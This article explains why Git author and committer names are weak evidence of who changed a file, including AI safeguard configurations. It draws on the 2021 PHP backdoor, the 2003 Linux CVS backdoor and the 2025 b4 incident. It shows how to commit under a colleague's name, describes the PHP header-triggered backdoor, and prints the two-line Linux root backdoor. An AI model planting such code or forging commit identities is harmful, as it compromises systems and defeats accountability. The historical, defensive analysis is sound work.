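# Forged commits and the reliability of version history as evidence of who changed an AI safeguard

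## What does a version-control history record about who made a change?

Version control stores files together with a history of their changes, so that a team can see how the files have changed and go back to earlier versions. Most programmers use a program called Git for this. About 97 percent of professional developers on the programming forum Stack Overflow use it, according to Holtgrave, Friedrich and colleagues in *Attributing Open-Source Contributions is Critical but Difficult*. The files and their history make up a repository, and each recorded change is called a commit. Teams usually keep a shared copy of the repository on a server, often on GitHub, the most popular hosting service.

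Every commit carries names and dates. The names can be wrong, though people tend to read the history as a record of who did what. In March 2021, two malicious changes entered the source code of the PHP programming language under the names of two maintainers who had not made them. Developers often keep the files that control an AI system's protections in repositories too, so the same problem of attribution (establishing which person, account or program made a change) arises for those files.

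### A change to a threshold

Suppose a company runs a chatbot behind a harmful-content classifier, a smaller model that gives each request a score from 0 to 1, with higher scores for requests more likely to be harmful. The service blocks every request that scores at or above a threshold, which is set to 0.80 in a text file. An engineer, Ines Falk, changes the threshold to 0.97. A request that scores 0.90, which the service would have blocked before, now reaches the chatbot.

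Filter rules and classifier thresholds like these make up a system's safeguard configuration. Keeping it in a repository lets engineers review a proposed change before it takes effect, run automated tests on it, and load the same version on every server. If the chatbot starts to misbehave after an update, the team can compare the old settings with the new ones and restore the old.

When Falk runs the command `git commit`, Git writes a small text record on her laptop. With invented and shortened identifiers, it looks like this:

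```
tree 9c41...e07a
parent 3fb2...81d6
author Ines Falk <ines.falk@example.com> 1772530320 +0000
committer Ines Falk <ines.falk@example.com> 1772530320 +0000

Raise blocking threshold to 0.97
```

Git's manual lists these five fields as required. The tree line identifies the state of all the files after the change, and the parent line identifies the previous commit. The next two lines give the author and the committer, each with a time in seconds since the start of 1970 (here 09:32 UTC on 3 March 2026). The message comes last, and Falk can write whatever she likes in it. Git stores the whole new file and compares it with the parent commit when someone asks to see the difference, so the record itself does not state that 0.80 became 0.97.

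So far the commit exists only on the laptop. To share it, Falk runs `git push`. The server checks that her computer holds her account's credentials and that the account has permission to write to the repository, then accepts the commit. None of the five fields records which account uploaded the commit.

### Author, committer and pusher

Git therefore involves three roles, and the evidence for them sits in different places.

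| Role | What the person or program does | Where the identity appears | Who controls that record |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Author | Writes the change | Author field of the commit | Whoever creates the commit |
| Committer | Records the change as a commit | Committer field of the commit | Whoever creates the commit |
| Pusher | Uploads the commit to the server | The server's push log, outside the commit | Whoever runs the server |

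Falk filled all three roles herself, but in other projects different people fill them. Contributors to the Linux kernel, for instance, send their changes by email, and one of a small group of maintainers turns them into commits, so the committer is not the author.

The author and committer names come from settings on the user's own machine. If Falk types `git config user.name "Omar Haddad"` and sets the email address to match, her next commit will carry her colleague's name in both fields. She doesn't need Haddad's password. GitHub's *Setting your username in Git* recommends the name setting to people who want to keep their real name private and tells them "you can use any text as your Git username". Git's manual page for the commit command says the name "has no effect on authentication" and lists other settings that replace the dates.

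Authentication happens only at the push. If Falk commits as Haddad and then pushes from her own account, the commit has Haddad's name on it and the server's log has Falk's. Most people will only ever see Haddad's name. GitHub links a commit to the profile of the registered account that matches the email address in the author field. Holtgrave and colleagues tested this by pushing a commit under the address of Dependabot, GitHub's automated account for proposing updates to software components. GitHub displayed it just as it displays Dependabot's real commits. GitHub does not notify users when someone else pushes commits with their addresses.

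GitHub knows about this and has defended it. In a statement that the same researchers quote, the company argued that crediting every commit to the person who pushed it would be incorrect. This is reasonable, since someone who uploads a week of a team's work did not write all of it. Holtgrave and colleagues collected 437,211 commits that GitHub users pushed to 7,546 repositories between April and July 2024, and the author, committer and pusher all traced back to the same account in only 30.1 percent of them. Much of the rest has an innocent explanation. For example, the software company JetBrains has a bot that commits and pushes its programmers' work to one of its public repositories. A mismatch between author and pusher is therefore weak evidence of forgery on its own, and an investigator has to know how a team normally works before drawing conclusions from it.

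### What the hash chain protects

Git does have strong protection against one kind of tampering, and people sometimes take it for protection against false names. It rests on a hash function, a calculation that turns data of any length into a short string of fixed length. The same data always gives the same string, and for practical purposes different data gives a different one. Git applies it in layers:

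1. Git hashes the contents of the threshold file. With 0.97 in place of 0.80, the file gets a new identifier.
2. Git lists the names and identifiers of the files in each directory and hashes the list. The new file identifier changes the identifier of its directory, and so on up to the top-level directory. That top identifier goes into the tree line of the commit.
3. Git hashes the commit itself, with its tree, parent, names, dates and message. The result is the commit hash, say `a71c...`.
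4. The next commit, whoever makes it, contains `a71c...` in its parent line, so its own hash depends on Falk's commit. The one after that depends on both.

Suppose that a month later someone changes the name on Falk's commit to Haddad's. The altered text gives a different hash, say `d05e...`. But the following commit still has `a71c...` as its parent, so the forger has to rewrite that one too, and every commit after it. Rapaport, Pautet and colleagues, in *Altered Histories in Version Control System Repositories*, call this a snowball effect. If a million later commits build on the altered one, all million get new identifiers.

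This makes the history easy to check. Anyone who wrote down the hash of the latest commit last week can look for that commit today, and if it is still in the chain, nothing before it has changed. The earlier hash has to come from a place the forger could not reach, such as a colleague's copy or an outside archive. Someone who first sees the repository after the rewriting cannot detect it from the chain alone, because every link still fits.

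The chain of hashes can't reveal that a name was false from the start. If Falk sets her name to Haddad before she commits, Git includes Haddad's name in the data it hashes and produces a valid commit hash. Git does not check the name against the identity of the person at the keyboard. Afterwards, the false name is as hard to change as a true one would have been, because correcting it would change the hash of every later commit.

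Falk's commit has no signature. A commit signature is an optional cryptographic mark that a committer adds with a private key, a secret file that only its owner should hold. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the private key approved that exact commit.

The chain is also only as strong as its hash function, according to LWN, a news site that covers Linux and free software. Git has always used SHA-1 by default. In 2017 and 2020 researchers published collision attacks on SHA-1, which produce two different pieces of data with the same hash. Chacon (2026), in *Git 3.0's upcoming SHA-256 default will be a costly mistake*, puts the cost of a collision at a few tens of thousands of dollars. The attacker has to prepare both versions in advance, get the harmless one accepted, and swap in the malicious one later.

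The Git project plans to make SHA-256, a stronger hash function than SHA-1, the default for new repositories in version 3.0. Chacon, a co-founder of GitHub, thinks the drawbacks of switching will far outweigh the benefits, because nobody has shown a practical way to exploit SHA-1's weakness in Git. The switch matters little for attribution, since SHA-256, like SHA-1, can hash a commit that carries a false name.

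### Branch pointers and force-pushes

A repository can hold many commits that are not part of the history people see. The visible history depends on a branch pointer, a movable label that marks one commit as the current end of a line of development. The main pointer is usually named `main`. To show the history, Git starts at the commit that `main` points to and follows each commit's parent back to the beginning. When Falk pushed her change, the server stored the new commit and moved `main` from `3fb2...` to `a71c...`.

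An ordinary push can only extend a branch. Git's manual says the commit at the old end must be an ancestor of the commit at the new end. A force-push turns that check off. A user with the necessary permission could force-push to point `main` at `d05e...`, the version of the commit with Haddad's name on it, or back at `3fb2...`, which would leave no trace of the threshold change in the visible history. The abandoned commit may remain on the server for a while, but Git can delete commits that no pointer leads to. Administrators can set a server to refuse force-pushes, and no option on the user's side can override that setting.

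Most rewriting of this kind is routine, such as tidying a proposed change before colleagues merge it. It is also fairly rare. Rapaport and colleagues compared successive archived copies of 111 million public repositories and found that 1.22 million of the repositories, about 1.1 percent, had lost commits between copies.

A push moves a pointer on the server, so the server can record the move. On the version of GitHub that companies host themselves, each push log entry lists the user who pushed, the branch, the network address, whether it was a force-push, and the hashes before and after, according to GitHub's *Viewing push logs*. The entry for the threshold change would show that Falk's account moved `main` from `3fb2...` to `a71c...`, whatever name she had put in the commit.

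GitHub's *Using the activity view to see changes to a repository* describes a page where anyone who can read a repository can see which account made each push or force-push. Until May 2023, users had to contact GitHub's support staff to see a repository's pushes, according to GitHub's *View repository pushes on the new activity view* (2023).

### Four questions about a changed safeguard

Suppose the company takes six weeks to notice that its chatbot is answering requests it used to refuse. Several people will want to know who changed the threshold, for different reasons. The company's investigator has to decide what to repair. If an intruder stole Falk's credentials, the company must replace them and search for whatever else the intruder touched, while a faulty script needs a different fix. An auditor will ask whether someone authorized to weaken a safeguard approved this change. A regulator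 may care most about whether the company chose to weaken the safeguard or failed to protect it.

Governments already take an interest in where software comes from. Holtgrave and colleagues point to two US documents that deal with software in general: a 2021 executive order on software supply chain security, and a 2024 form from the cybersecurity agency CISA that treats provenance, the record of a program's origins, as a precondition for that security.

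"Who changed it?" combines several questions that need separate evidence. The easiest to answer is what changed. Comparing Falk's commit with its parent shows the file, the line, and the old and new numbers. The hash chain makes this record hard to falsify without being detected by anyone who holds a previously recorded hash.

The two dates in the commit don't reliably show when the value changed, because Falk's laptop supplied both and she could have set them to any day. The time in the push log is better evidence because it comes from the server, but it records only when the change reached the repository. The chatbot began using 0.97 when the company next loaded the configuration into the live service, which could have been minutes or weeks later.

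Through which account the change arrived is a question for the push log alone. The author field does not answer it.

An entry with Falk's account in it does little to show whose decision the change was. Falk may have thought the classifier was blocking too many innocent requests, or her manager may have told her to raise the number. A colleague may have used her unlocked laptop, or an intruder may have used a copy of her key. A faulty deployment script that runs with her credentials may have overwritten the file, or an AI coding agent working under her account may have edited it during another task. Any of these could leave the same commit and the same line in the push log.

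## What happened in the 2021 PHP incident, and how was it reconstructed?

PHP is a programming language that web servers use to build pages. Almost 80 percent of websites used it in 2021, according to *Hackers backdoor PHP source code after internal repo hack* (Cimpanu, 2021). Its source code is public, but only a limited group of developers can change it. In March 2021 somebody used the names of two of those developers to plant malicious code. The maintainers gave three different explanations of the intrusion within ten days, changing their minds each time they checked a record they hadn't seen before.

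Most of what is known about the case comes from Nikita Popov, one of PHP's most active maintainers and one of the two people whose names the attacker used. Popov (2021) announced the intrusion on PHP's public mailing list on the night of 28–29 March, in a message titled *Changes to Git commit workflow*. He corrected much of that message in a long follow-up on 6 April.

### Two commits under borrowed names

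The PHP project ran its own Git server, git.php.net, and GitHub held only a mirror, a secondary copy of the code. Developers with write access could push changes straight to the server, and their colleagues reviewed them only after they had entered the repository.

At 03:58 UTC on Sunday 28 March, a commit titled "[skip-ci] Fix typo" arrived. Below the title, the attacker had written that the commit fixed a minor typo. Developers put "[skip-ci]" in a title to make automated testing systems ignore a change too small to need testing. The commit's author and committer fields both named Rasmus Lerdorf, who created PHP.

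The commit in fact added eleven lines to the part of PHP that compresses web pages before sending them. When a browser requests a page, it also sends headers, which are short labelled lines giving details such as the browser's name. According to Ducklin (2021), in *PHP web language narrowly avoids “backdoor” supply chain attack*, the new code looked for a header with a slightly misspelled name. If the header's contents began with a particular word, the server would run the rest as a program. Anyone who knew the word could run commands on a website that used this version of PHP, typically with all the rights of the web server.

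The word was "zerodium", the name of a company that bought undisclosed software flaws. The inserted code also contained the phrase "REMOVETHIS: sold to zerodium, mid 2017". Zerodium's chief executive, Chaouki Bekrar, denied any involvement, according to *PHP Compromised* (2021), an analysis by Wordfence, which makes security software for websites. The phrase is not evidence of where the code came from, because the attacker could write anything there, as in the author field.

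Cimpanu credits Michael Voříšek, a Czech software engineer, with spotting the malicious code first. TechRadar's *Someone just tried to add a security backdoor in the PHP language* reports that a developer asked Lerdorf to explain what he had apparently committed. According to WeLiveSecurity (2021), the news site of the security company ESET, Popov told reporters that the discovery came during a routine review. He reverted the commit by adding a new one that undid it. His revert is dated 09:16 UTC, a little over five hours after the malicious push.

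The backdoor reappeared at 16:13 UTC, this time in a commit under Popov's own name. The commit was titled `Revert "Revert "[skip-ci] Fix typo""`, as if he had changed his mind about removing it. Another maintainer, Levi Morrison, reverted it at 17:53 UTC, according to the timeline in *Update to recent git.php.net incident* (2021) from PHP.Watch, a news site that follows the language. Across the two periods, the backdoor was in PHP's development code for about seven hours.

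PHP.Watch and several maintainers used their own copies of the repository to confirm that nobody had tampered with the older history, according to PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021). The attacker and the people who reverted the malicious commits had only added new commits to the end of the chain, so both malicious commits remain in PHP's history under the names of Lerdorf and Popov.

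The maintainers quickly knew that the names were false because both men were available to say so and their colleagues believed them. The code was so crude that their denials were easier to believe, since neither man had an obvious reason to add it to his own project under his own name. But nothing in the commits would have cleared either of them, and a guilty maintainer would have denied it too.

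### The "Signed-off-by" line

The first commit's message ended with the line "Signed-off-by: Rasmus Lerdorf" and Lerdorf's email address. This line is ordinary text, though it is easily mistaken for a signature. Git adds it when a user runs `git commit --signoff`, taking the name and address from the same settings that fill the committer field. Anyone can also type it by hand. The Linux kernel project asks contributors to include the line to declare that they have the legal right to submit their code, not to prove their identity.

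The sign-off only repeated Lerdorf's name, which was already in the author and committer fields. A forger can type a sign-off but needs the signer's private key to make a commit signature, and PHP did not require signatures in March 2021.

Some press coverage blurred the difference. The Stack (2021) wrote that the hackers had signed the commits off as if known PHP developers had made them. WeLiveSecurity described the second commit as disguised to look signed off by Popov. That commit apparently had no sign-off line, because Wordfence found that it had a title but no description.

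### From a stolen account to a breached server

When Popov saw the first commit, he assumed that someone had stolen Lerdorf's account, and he revoked its access to the repository. In his follow-up, Popov wrote that this "didn't really make sense". He had no reason then to think the push had come through Lerdorf's account, because any account with access to the repository could have pushed a commit with Lerdorf's name on it. Popov knew Git well, but under pressure he still assumed that the named author had pushed the commit.

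The attacker had in fact used Lerdorf's account, so Popov had closed the right one, though for a poor reason. Seven hours after the revert, the attacker pushed the second commit through a different account.

Popov then tried to find out who had pushed the malicious commits. The project controlled access to its Git server with a program called gitolite. Developers connected over SSH, a secure protocol in which each user proves who they are with a private key. Gitolite checked what the key's owner was allowed to do and kept a log. Every push should have left a log entry for git-receive-pack, the program a Git server uses to accept uploads. Popov found entries for all the surrounding commits but none for the malicious ones.

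The neighbouring entries ruled out a general logging failure. Popov correctly concluded that the two commits had bypassed gitolite entirely. He then took the missing entries as a likely sign that somebody had broken into the server, because an intruder who controls the machine can write commits directly to its disk. Less than seven hours after the second push, he told the mailing list that "everything points towards a compromise of the git.php.net server", rather than an individual's account.

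That conclusion depended on the gitolite log covering every permitted way to push, but the server also accepted pushes over HTTPS. For those pushes, the Apache web server required a username and password, then passed the upload to a standard Git program without going through gitolite, so the gitolite log had no record of them. The project had set up this route deliberately, but Popov did not know about it until after the incident.

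Other people in the project did know about the HTTPS address. *Git on y3.php.net*, a set of undated notes for the project's server administrators, includes it in the steps for setting up a new repository. In an old mailing list thread, a developer who signs as Sara posted the server's reply to her push to the same address, and another developer, Hannes, suggested that she switch to SSH. Lerdorf also took part in that thread. The list is public, so an outsider could have found the address there, and the attacker's use of it does not indicate inside knowledge.

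### What the access log showed

The web server kept its own access log, which did contain both pushes. Popov published fourteen lines from it, with the network addresses blacked out. Each line gives the username that the visitor's computer supplied, the time, the request and a code for the outcome. When Git pushes over HTTPS, it first asks the server which commit each branch currently points to, and then uploads the new commits. The table below summarizes the fourteen lines.

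| Time (UTC−7) | Username supplied | Request | Outcome |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 27 March, 19:19:23 and 19:19:28 | rasmus@ (rest blacked out) | Read the repository | Refused twice |
| 27 March, 20:56:51 | rasmus | Push, first step | Accepted |
| 27 March, 20:58:13 | rasmus | Push, upload | Accepted |
| 28 March, 09:09:15 and 09:09:18 | nikita.ppv | Read the repository | Refused twice |
| 28 March, 09:09:35 and 09:09:36 | nikitappv | Read the repository | Refused twice |
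| 28 March, 09:09:50 and 09:09:53 | nikita | Read the repository | Refused twice |
| 28 March, 09:11:31 | nikic | Push, first step | Refused twice |
| 28 March, 09:13:28 | nikic | Push, first step | Accepted |
| 28 March, 09:13:39 | nikic | Push, upload | Accepted |

Reports disagree about when the attack began because of time zones. Wordfence dates the first commit to Saturday 27 March, and PHP.Watch dates it to Sunday 28 March. The server's clock was seven hours behind UTC, so it recorded the upload at 8:58 p.m. on Saturday, when it was 5:58 a.m. on Sunday in central Europe.

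The commit's own date is 05:57:07 on 28 March, in a time zone two hours ahead of UTC. That is 66 seconds before the upload recorded in the server's log, which suggests that the attacker did not falsify the date. The time zone fits central Europe in summer, but it is weaker evidence because anyone can change the time zone in their computer's settings.

The wrong usernames are the best evidence in the log that the visitor was neither Lerdorf nor Popov. Popov would hardly have needed three wrong guesses to reach "nikic", his own account name. The first guess, "nikita.ppv", is the start of the email address he used on the public mailing list. An outsider who knew that address but not the account name might well have guessed this way. A maintainer could have staged the same guesses to look like an outsider, though nobody seems to have suspected that.

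Popov noted that the attacker made only a few guesses and got in once the username was right. The log mostly matches this account, except that the server rejected the correct username, "nikic", twice at 09:11:31 before accepting it two minutes later. The attacker could have mistyped the password or had more than one to try. The log doesn't contain the passwords, so it isn't enough to determine which.

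The access log therefore identified the accounts that pushed the commits, and both accounts matched the forged names. "rasmus" pushed the commit in Lerdorf's name, and "nikic" pushed the one in Popov's. An auditor who compared the author, committer and pusher of each commit would have found that they matched, though all three identified the wrong person. Holtgrave and colleagues found that these fields differ in many honest projects. The log recorded the accounts correctly, but the attacker had obtained both men's passwords or something that worked in their place.

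### The suspected password leak

Popov's best guess was that someone had copied the user database of master.php.net, a separate machine that managed the developers' accounts, but he said he had no specific evidence of this. The machine ran very old code on a very old operating system, and he wrote that a vulnerability there "would not be terribly surprising".

The way the machine stored passwords would have made such a leak serious. A well-run service stores only a hash of each password, made with a deliberately slow function so that a thief needs a long time to test millions of likely passwords against the stolen hashes. The HTTPS route used an older login scheme, HTTP Digest authentication, which required hashes in a particular format that Popov described as essentially plain MD5. MD5 is an old function that modern hardware computes extremely fast. PHP.Watch calls it trivial to recover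 a password from such a hash, which is fair for short or common passwords but overstates the risk for long random ones.

Popov himself raised a problem with this theory. The database would have contained the usernames, so a thief who had it shouldn't have needed to guess them. The guessing would make more sense if the passwords had been stolen from another website, because the thief would then know a person's email address and password but not their PHP username. For that to work, both men must have reused their PHP passwords elsewhere, and Popov's messages contain no evidence for or against this.

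Others reported Popov's suspicion more confidently than he had. The Daily Swig, a security news site, wrote that the team now believed the database "was leaked", although Popov had only called a leak possible. It also reported that how the attacker got in was unclear. PHP.Watch wrote that Popov had identified the old software and web configuration on master.php.net as the root cause, but he had described them only as a plausible weakness.

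### What the project changed

Shortly after the second commit, Popov and his colleagues decided to stop using git.php.net, which they still believed someone had broken into. The copies on GitHub became the official repositories. To push changes, developers now had to belong to the project's GitHub organization, a requirement that replaced a home-made permission system called karma. Membership required two-factor authentication, which asks for a second proof of identity, such as a code from a phone, in addition to the password.

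The theory that the server had been compromised made the move to GitHub look urgent, but Popov also gave reasons that did not depend on it. Finding the cause of the break-in and then building a new server would have delayed PHP's development. Most of the repositories were already copied to GitHub, much of the work was happening there, and he regarded the project's own Git servers mostly as a liability. The move also suited the later explanation, a stolen password, perhaps better than the original one, because a password alone does not get an intruder past two-factor authentication.

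After Popov found the HTTPS pushes, the project repaired its account system. It moved master.php.net to a new machine with up-to-date software, renamed it main.php.net and reset every password. It now stores passwords with bcrypt, a deliberately slow hash function. The programmers also rewrote database queries to make it harder for an attacker to insert commands into them. The old Git server, and an even older one for a system called Subversion, stopped accepting changes. With no password-based pushes left to support, the project no longer needed the weak hashes.

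On the mailing list, several developers asked for compulsory commit signatures, so that committing would require a private key as well as a password. Lerdorf answered that the project could require signatures for PHP's main source code and leave them optional elsewhere for now. It is unclear whether this became a rule. Lerdorf tweeted on 29 March that the project had moved to GitHub "requiring 2FA and signed commits" (reproduced in PHP Architect's *About PHP’s Compromised Git Commit*, 2021). But PHP.Watch reported at the time that two-factor authentication was compulsory and signing was only encouraged.

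Max Semenik, another developer, went further and proposed forbidding direct pushes, so that someone would have to review every change before it entered the repository. Others objected that this would slow down trivial corrections and automated updates. It would also complicate carrying fixes from older versions of PHP into newer ones. George P. Banyard added that some of the automated tests failed at random, so requiring every change to pass them could block good work. He preferred to require signatures on direct pushes.

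One developer also recalled that a push to PHP's website repository used to go live automatically. If it still did, an intruder could change the public site with a single push, so he suggested turning off automatic publication for a while. Changes to the language itself reached the public long after a push, which gave reviewers time to catch the forged commits.

### No release contained the backdoor

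Wordfence reports that Popov said the changes were on the development branch for PHP 8.1, which was due at the end of the year, and had not entered any release. The project told users in its website's *News Archive* (2021) that developers had noticed and reverted the commits immediately and that they "never reached end users". One commit stayed in place for more than five hours, so "immediately" is an overstatement, but the claim about releases is correct. The project also postponed two routine updates, PHP 8.0.4 and 7.4.17, by two weeks to examine the existing code.

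Someone could still have downloaded the development version that Sunday, built it and put it on a public web server. Ducklin thought that probably no one had done so, except perhaps the attackers.

### Open questions and a theory that outlived its withdrawal

Nobody appears to have publicly identified the attacker, and how the attacker could log in as Lerdorf and Popov remains unexplained. Popov's message of 6 April is still the fullest account of the evidence, and in it he describes a leak of the database only as a possibility.

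The motive is unknown too. Wordfence thought one person had done it, perhaps as a prank, because the attacker had hardly tried to hide the code and had mentioned Zerodium conspicuously. This is reasonable speculation, but crude code doesn't show how many people were involved. A commenter on Wordfence's article suggested that the commits could have been a distraction from something else. PHP.Watch warned at the time that an intact history did not guarantee that there were no other backdoors.

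The PHP project first said that hackers had breached its Git server, but Popov withdrew that explanation nine days after the second commit. "We no longer believe the git.php.net server has been compromised," he wrote at the top of his follow-up. News reports from the end of March predate the withdrawal, and PHP.Watch later marked its original article as outdated. Many other descriptions of the case still say the server was breached. *PHP language source code compromise attempt*, from the antivirus company Kaspersky, presents the breach as fact and reverses the order of the two commits.

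The old version also remains in reference works that engineers use to learn from past attacks. The Cloud Native Computing Foundation (CNCF), an industry body for open-source software, keeps a catalogue of such attacks. Its PHP entry, *Compromise of PHP’s development team self-hosted Git server*, has the withdrawn theory in its title and treats how the server was breached as the remaining question. Version 1.0 of SLSA, a widely used set of rules for protecting software from tampering, used PHP as its example of a compromised source repository. According to SLSA's *Supply chain threats*, a better-protected source-code platform would have been a much harder target.

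That advice is still partly right after the correction, because requiring two-factor authentication would have made it harder to enter the platform with a stolen password. But a team that followed the catalogue's account after a similar attack would start by searching its Git server for an intruder. In PHP's case, the useful evidence was in the web server's access log, and the suspected machine was the one that stored the passwords.

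## In what other cases did a repository name the wrong person?

The PHP attacker logged in to the accounts of the two men whose names went on the commits. False names have got into other repositories in other ways. In one case somebody edited files directly on a server, in another a maintenance tool copied a name where it did not belong, and in a third an attacker used made-up names of automated accounts.

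| Case | Name in the record | What exposed the error | Who or what was responsible |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Linux kernel, November 2003 | David Miller, a kernel developer | A nightly comparison with a second copy | Unknown |
| Linux kernel, May 2025 | Linus Torvalds, as committer | Different commit hashes in Torvalds's own copy | A tool called b4, which Kees Cook had run |
| Megalodon campaign, May 2026 | Invented automation names such as "build-bot" | Malicious releases of a package built from one of the repositories | No publicly known culprit |

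### A back door in a copy of the Linux kernel

The kernel is the part of the Linux operating system that controls the hardware and what each user may do. In 2003 Linus Torvalds, who created the kernel and makes the final decision on what goes into it, kept the master copy in BitKeeper, a commercial version-control system from a company called BitMover. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so BitMover also converted the code to CVS, an older free system, and published that copy on a public server. Changes were supposed to go only from BitKeeper to CVS.

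CVS keeps a separate log for each file and has no chain of hashes, so anyone who can write to the server's disk can add an entry to one file's log without changing anything else.

On 5 November 2003, Larry McVoy of BitMover reported such a case to the Linux kernel mailing list in *BK2CVS problem* (McVoy, 2003). He had found three entries in the log of `exit.c` that had not come from BitKeeper. All three were dated the day before and credited to "davem", David Miller's username. The first added two lines and had no message. The second removed 58 lines nineteen minutes later, and the third put 58 lines back two minutes after that, with an apology for having worked on the wrong file. The last two may have been a real mistake, or an attempt to make the latest log entries look like a harmless one.

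These were the two added lines:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The two lines were in `wait4`, a function that a program calls to wait for another program to finish. They would have let anyone who could run a program on the machine take full control of it by calling `wait4` with an odd combination of two options. On a quick read, they look like a check that returns an error if user number 0 asks for that combination. User 0 is root, the administrator, who may do anything on the machine. But the code used `=`, which assigns a value in C, instead of `==`, which compares two values, so it made the current user root instead of checking whether the user was root. The second line, which returned the error, would never have run, because C treats the result of assigning zero as false.

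In a 2013 post, the technology policy blog Freedom to Tinker called the change a definite attempt at a back door. Confusing the two operators is a common mistake, and one commenter suggested that a tired programmer could have typed it by accident. Another replied that the corrected check would have no purpose, since it would stop only root from using a harmless combination of options. That reply is persuasive, and a tired programmer would also have had to get the lines into a copy that nobody was supposed to edit.

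BitMover caught the change with an automatic routine, which McVoy described to the list in four steps:

1. A machine inside the company fetched the current BitKeeper version.
2. The same company network converted it to CVS and kept the result.
3. The routine copied the updated files to the public server.
4. It computed a checksum (a short number that changes if the file changes) for the files in both places, compared them, and sent an email if they differed.

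The nightly comparison showed that `exit.c` did not match, and McVoy then looked at the file's log. BitMover's converter ended each entry with a line such as "(Logical change 1.14141)", which pointed to the BitKeeper change it came from. The three entries under Miller's name had no such line. The forger had either overlooked this line or had no genuine BitKeeper change to point to.

Freedom to Tinker reverses this order, saying that McVoy first noticed the missing pointer, and describes it as a pointer to a record of approval. McVoy's own account is better evidence. The order matters in practice because somebody has to read the log of the right file to notice a missing line, while the checksums covered every file every night.

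McVoy repaired the file within 24 hours, after spending part of the day checking that his own converter was not at fault. He still didn't know what the two lines did. His first message said the change was "not a big deal", though annoying for people who used the CVS copy. About an hour and a half later, he posted the lines because a reader asked to see them, and within half an hour other developers had recognized a back door. The comparison had caught the change, but McVoy, an experienced programmer, admitted that he had missed the single equals sign that made it dangerous.

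It is less clear how close the back door came to a release. Torvalds replied in McVoy's thread that it had no route into the kernel, because code arrived only through patches emailed to him or through BitKeeper, and people who merged through BitKeeper did not use the CVS copy. McVoy thought a CVS user might have unknowingly included it in a patch. This was unlikely, because a patch normally contains only the lines its author changed, but a developer who compared the CVS copy with an official release could have included the back door in the resulting patch. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, saw a risk if any Linux distributor built its product from the CVS copy.

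McVoy's evidence that Miller was innocent was that "Dave swears up and down that it wasn't him". He also wrote that Dave had looked at the server and seen signs of an attempted break-in. Both remarks seem to refer to Miller. If so, the person named on the change was also the first to report evidence for the explanation that cleared him. Nobody in the thread suspected him, and there is no reason to. But his colleagues, like Lerdorf's and Popov's, relied on what they knew of him, because nothing in the log showed that he was innocent.

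The developer Andreas Dilger asked for a way to prove that a change marked "davem" came from the real David Miller. Ts'o had wanted this for years. He wrote that BitKeeper should have a digital signature on each changeset, its equivalent of a commit, so that anyone could check every change at any time without relying on Torvalds. He added that email had a similar weakness, because someone who convincingly forged a message from a trusted developer might get a small malicious patch past Torvalds. McVoy agreed and said BitMover had a design ready but had been waiting for "some event to trigger it".

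McVoy asked whoever was responsible to step forward. He suspected that the intruder had either changed the file directly on the server or come in through CVS's network login service. Ten years later, Freedom to Tinker considered whether the US National Security Agency had done it. It noted that many others had the skill and motive, and concluded that nobody would ever know without a confession or a leaked document.

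### The accusation against Kees Cook

Torvalds wrote Git in 2005 to replace BitKeeper. Twenty years later Git led him to accuse a colleague wrongly.

On 31 May 2025, Kees Cook, who maintains code that hardens the kernel against attack, asked Torvalds to merge four commits. *Hardening fixes lead to hard questions* (Corbet, 2025) describes the request as routine. The exchange that followed is in the thread *hardening fixes for v6.16-rc1* on the kernel's public mailing list.

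Torvalds found a commit in Cook's repository that listed Torvalds as its committer, with the hash `f8b59a0f90a2`. He had made a similar commit, but its hash was `9d230d500b0e`. He told Cook, "You seem to have actively maliciously modified your tree completely," in a message that Cook (2025) quoted in his reply. Torvalds refused to accept anything more from him without an explanation. He also asked Konstantin Ryabitsev, who looks after kernel.org, the site where most kernel maintainers keep their repositories, to disable Cook's account immediately, and Ryabitsev did so.

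Torvalds (2025) explained his reasoning a few hours later. Cook's branch contained 330 merge commits (commits that join two lines of development) that listed Torvalds as both author and committer, but none came from Torvalds's own repository. It also had more than 6,000 copies of other people's commits. Developers often copy commits by rebasing, which replays them on top of a newer starting point. An ordinary rebase puts the name of the person who runs it in the committer field, but these copies still had the original names. Since no normal command would do this, Torvalds thought it "almost has to be intentional", although he allowed that some terrible script might have done it.

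Cook first said he had no idea what had happened but suspected a failing disk, from which he had been trying to rebuild his repositories. Torvalds replied, correctly, that a damaged disk does not produce thousands of well-formed commits. Cook was innocent, but a mistaken first guess can look like a cover story to a suspicious reader.

In his next message, Cook defended himself by citing his record of asking Torvalds before deliberately doing anything strange with Git. He had recently constructed a commit whose hash began with the same characters as that of the first commit in the kernel's Git history, and had emailed Torvalds privately about it. The example was only a partial defense, because it also showed that he knew how to make unusual commits.

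A reconstruction that Cook posted two hours later cleared him. Git keeps a reflog on each user's machine, a private list of the commits that the user's branches have pointed to. Cook compared his reflog, entry by entry, with the list of commands he had typed. The false commits first appeared after he ran `b4 trailers`.

B4 is a program that Ryabitsev maintains to help kernel developers handle patches sent by email. Its `b4 trailers` command adds reviewers' emailed approvals to commit messages. Cook had wanted to add one approval, from Marco Elver, to a commit three places from the end of his branch, which required rewriting only that commit and the few after it. Instead, b4 displayed a message that it was looking for approvals for 39 commits, with a prompt to press Enter or cancel. Cook missed the warning and pressed Enter. B4 then ran git-filter-repo, a program for rewriting whole histories,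 which finished in less than four seconds.

Cook ran the command again from the same starting point and got the same false commits, with identical hashes. This proved that the command produced exactly the commits Torvalds had complained about. The hashes matched only because git-filter-repo kept the original dates instead of stamping each copy with the time of the rewrite.

About twenty hours after the accusation, Ryabitsev (2025) wrote that he was "100% convinced that there was no malicious intent" and restored the account. He apologized for his tool's part in the incident. Until then, the evidence had come from Cook's own computer, where Cook could have altered both the reflog and the command list. But Cook also posted a short recipe for reproducing the fault from public commits alone, and Ryabitsev reproduced it himself later that day, according to Cook's reply to him.

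Other maintainers had the same problem. Christian Brauner (2025) wrote that b4 had rewritten his commits several times. He usually caught it in trial merges, and once his colleague Vlastimil Babka noticed a problem in their shared work. Babka (2025) recreated that episode, starting with a merge commit that had a valid signature. After b4 ran, the commit had the same names and dates, to the second, but a new hash and no signature.

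Babka's test also suggests how a warning about 39 commits could be followed by more than 6,000 copies. B4 had rewritten both the merge and the commits it brought in from another maintainer. Kernel merges bring together long histories, so losing one signature could cause thousands of later commits to be rewritten. Torvalds had examined one copy and noticed that it was missing signature information but otherwise looked identical to the original.

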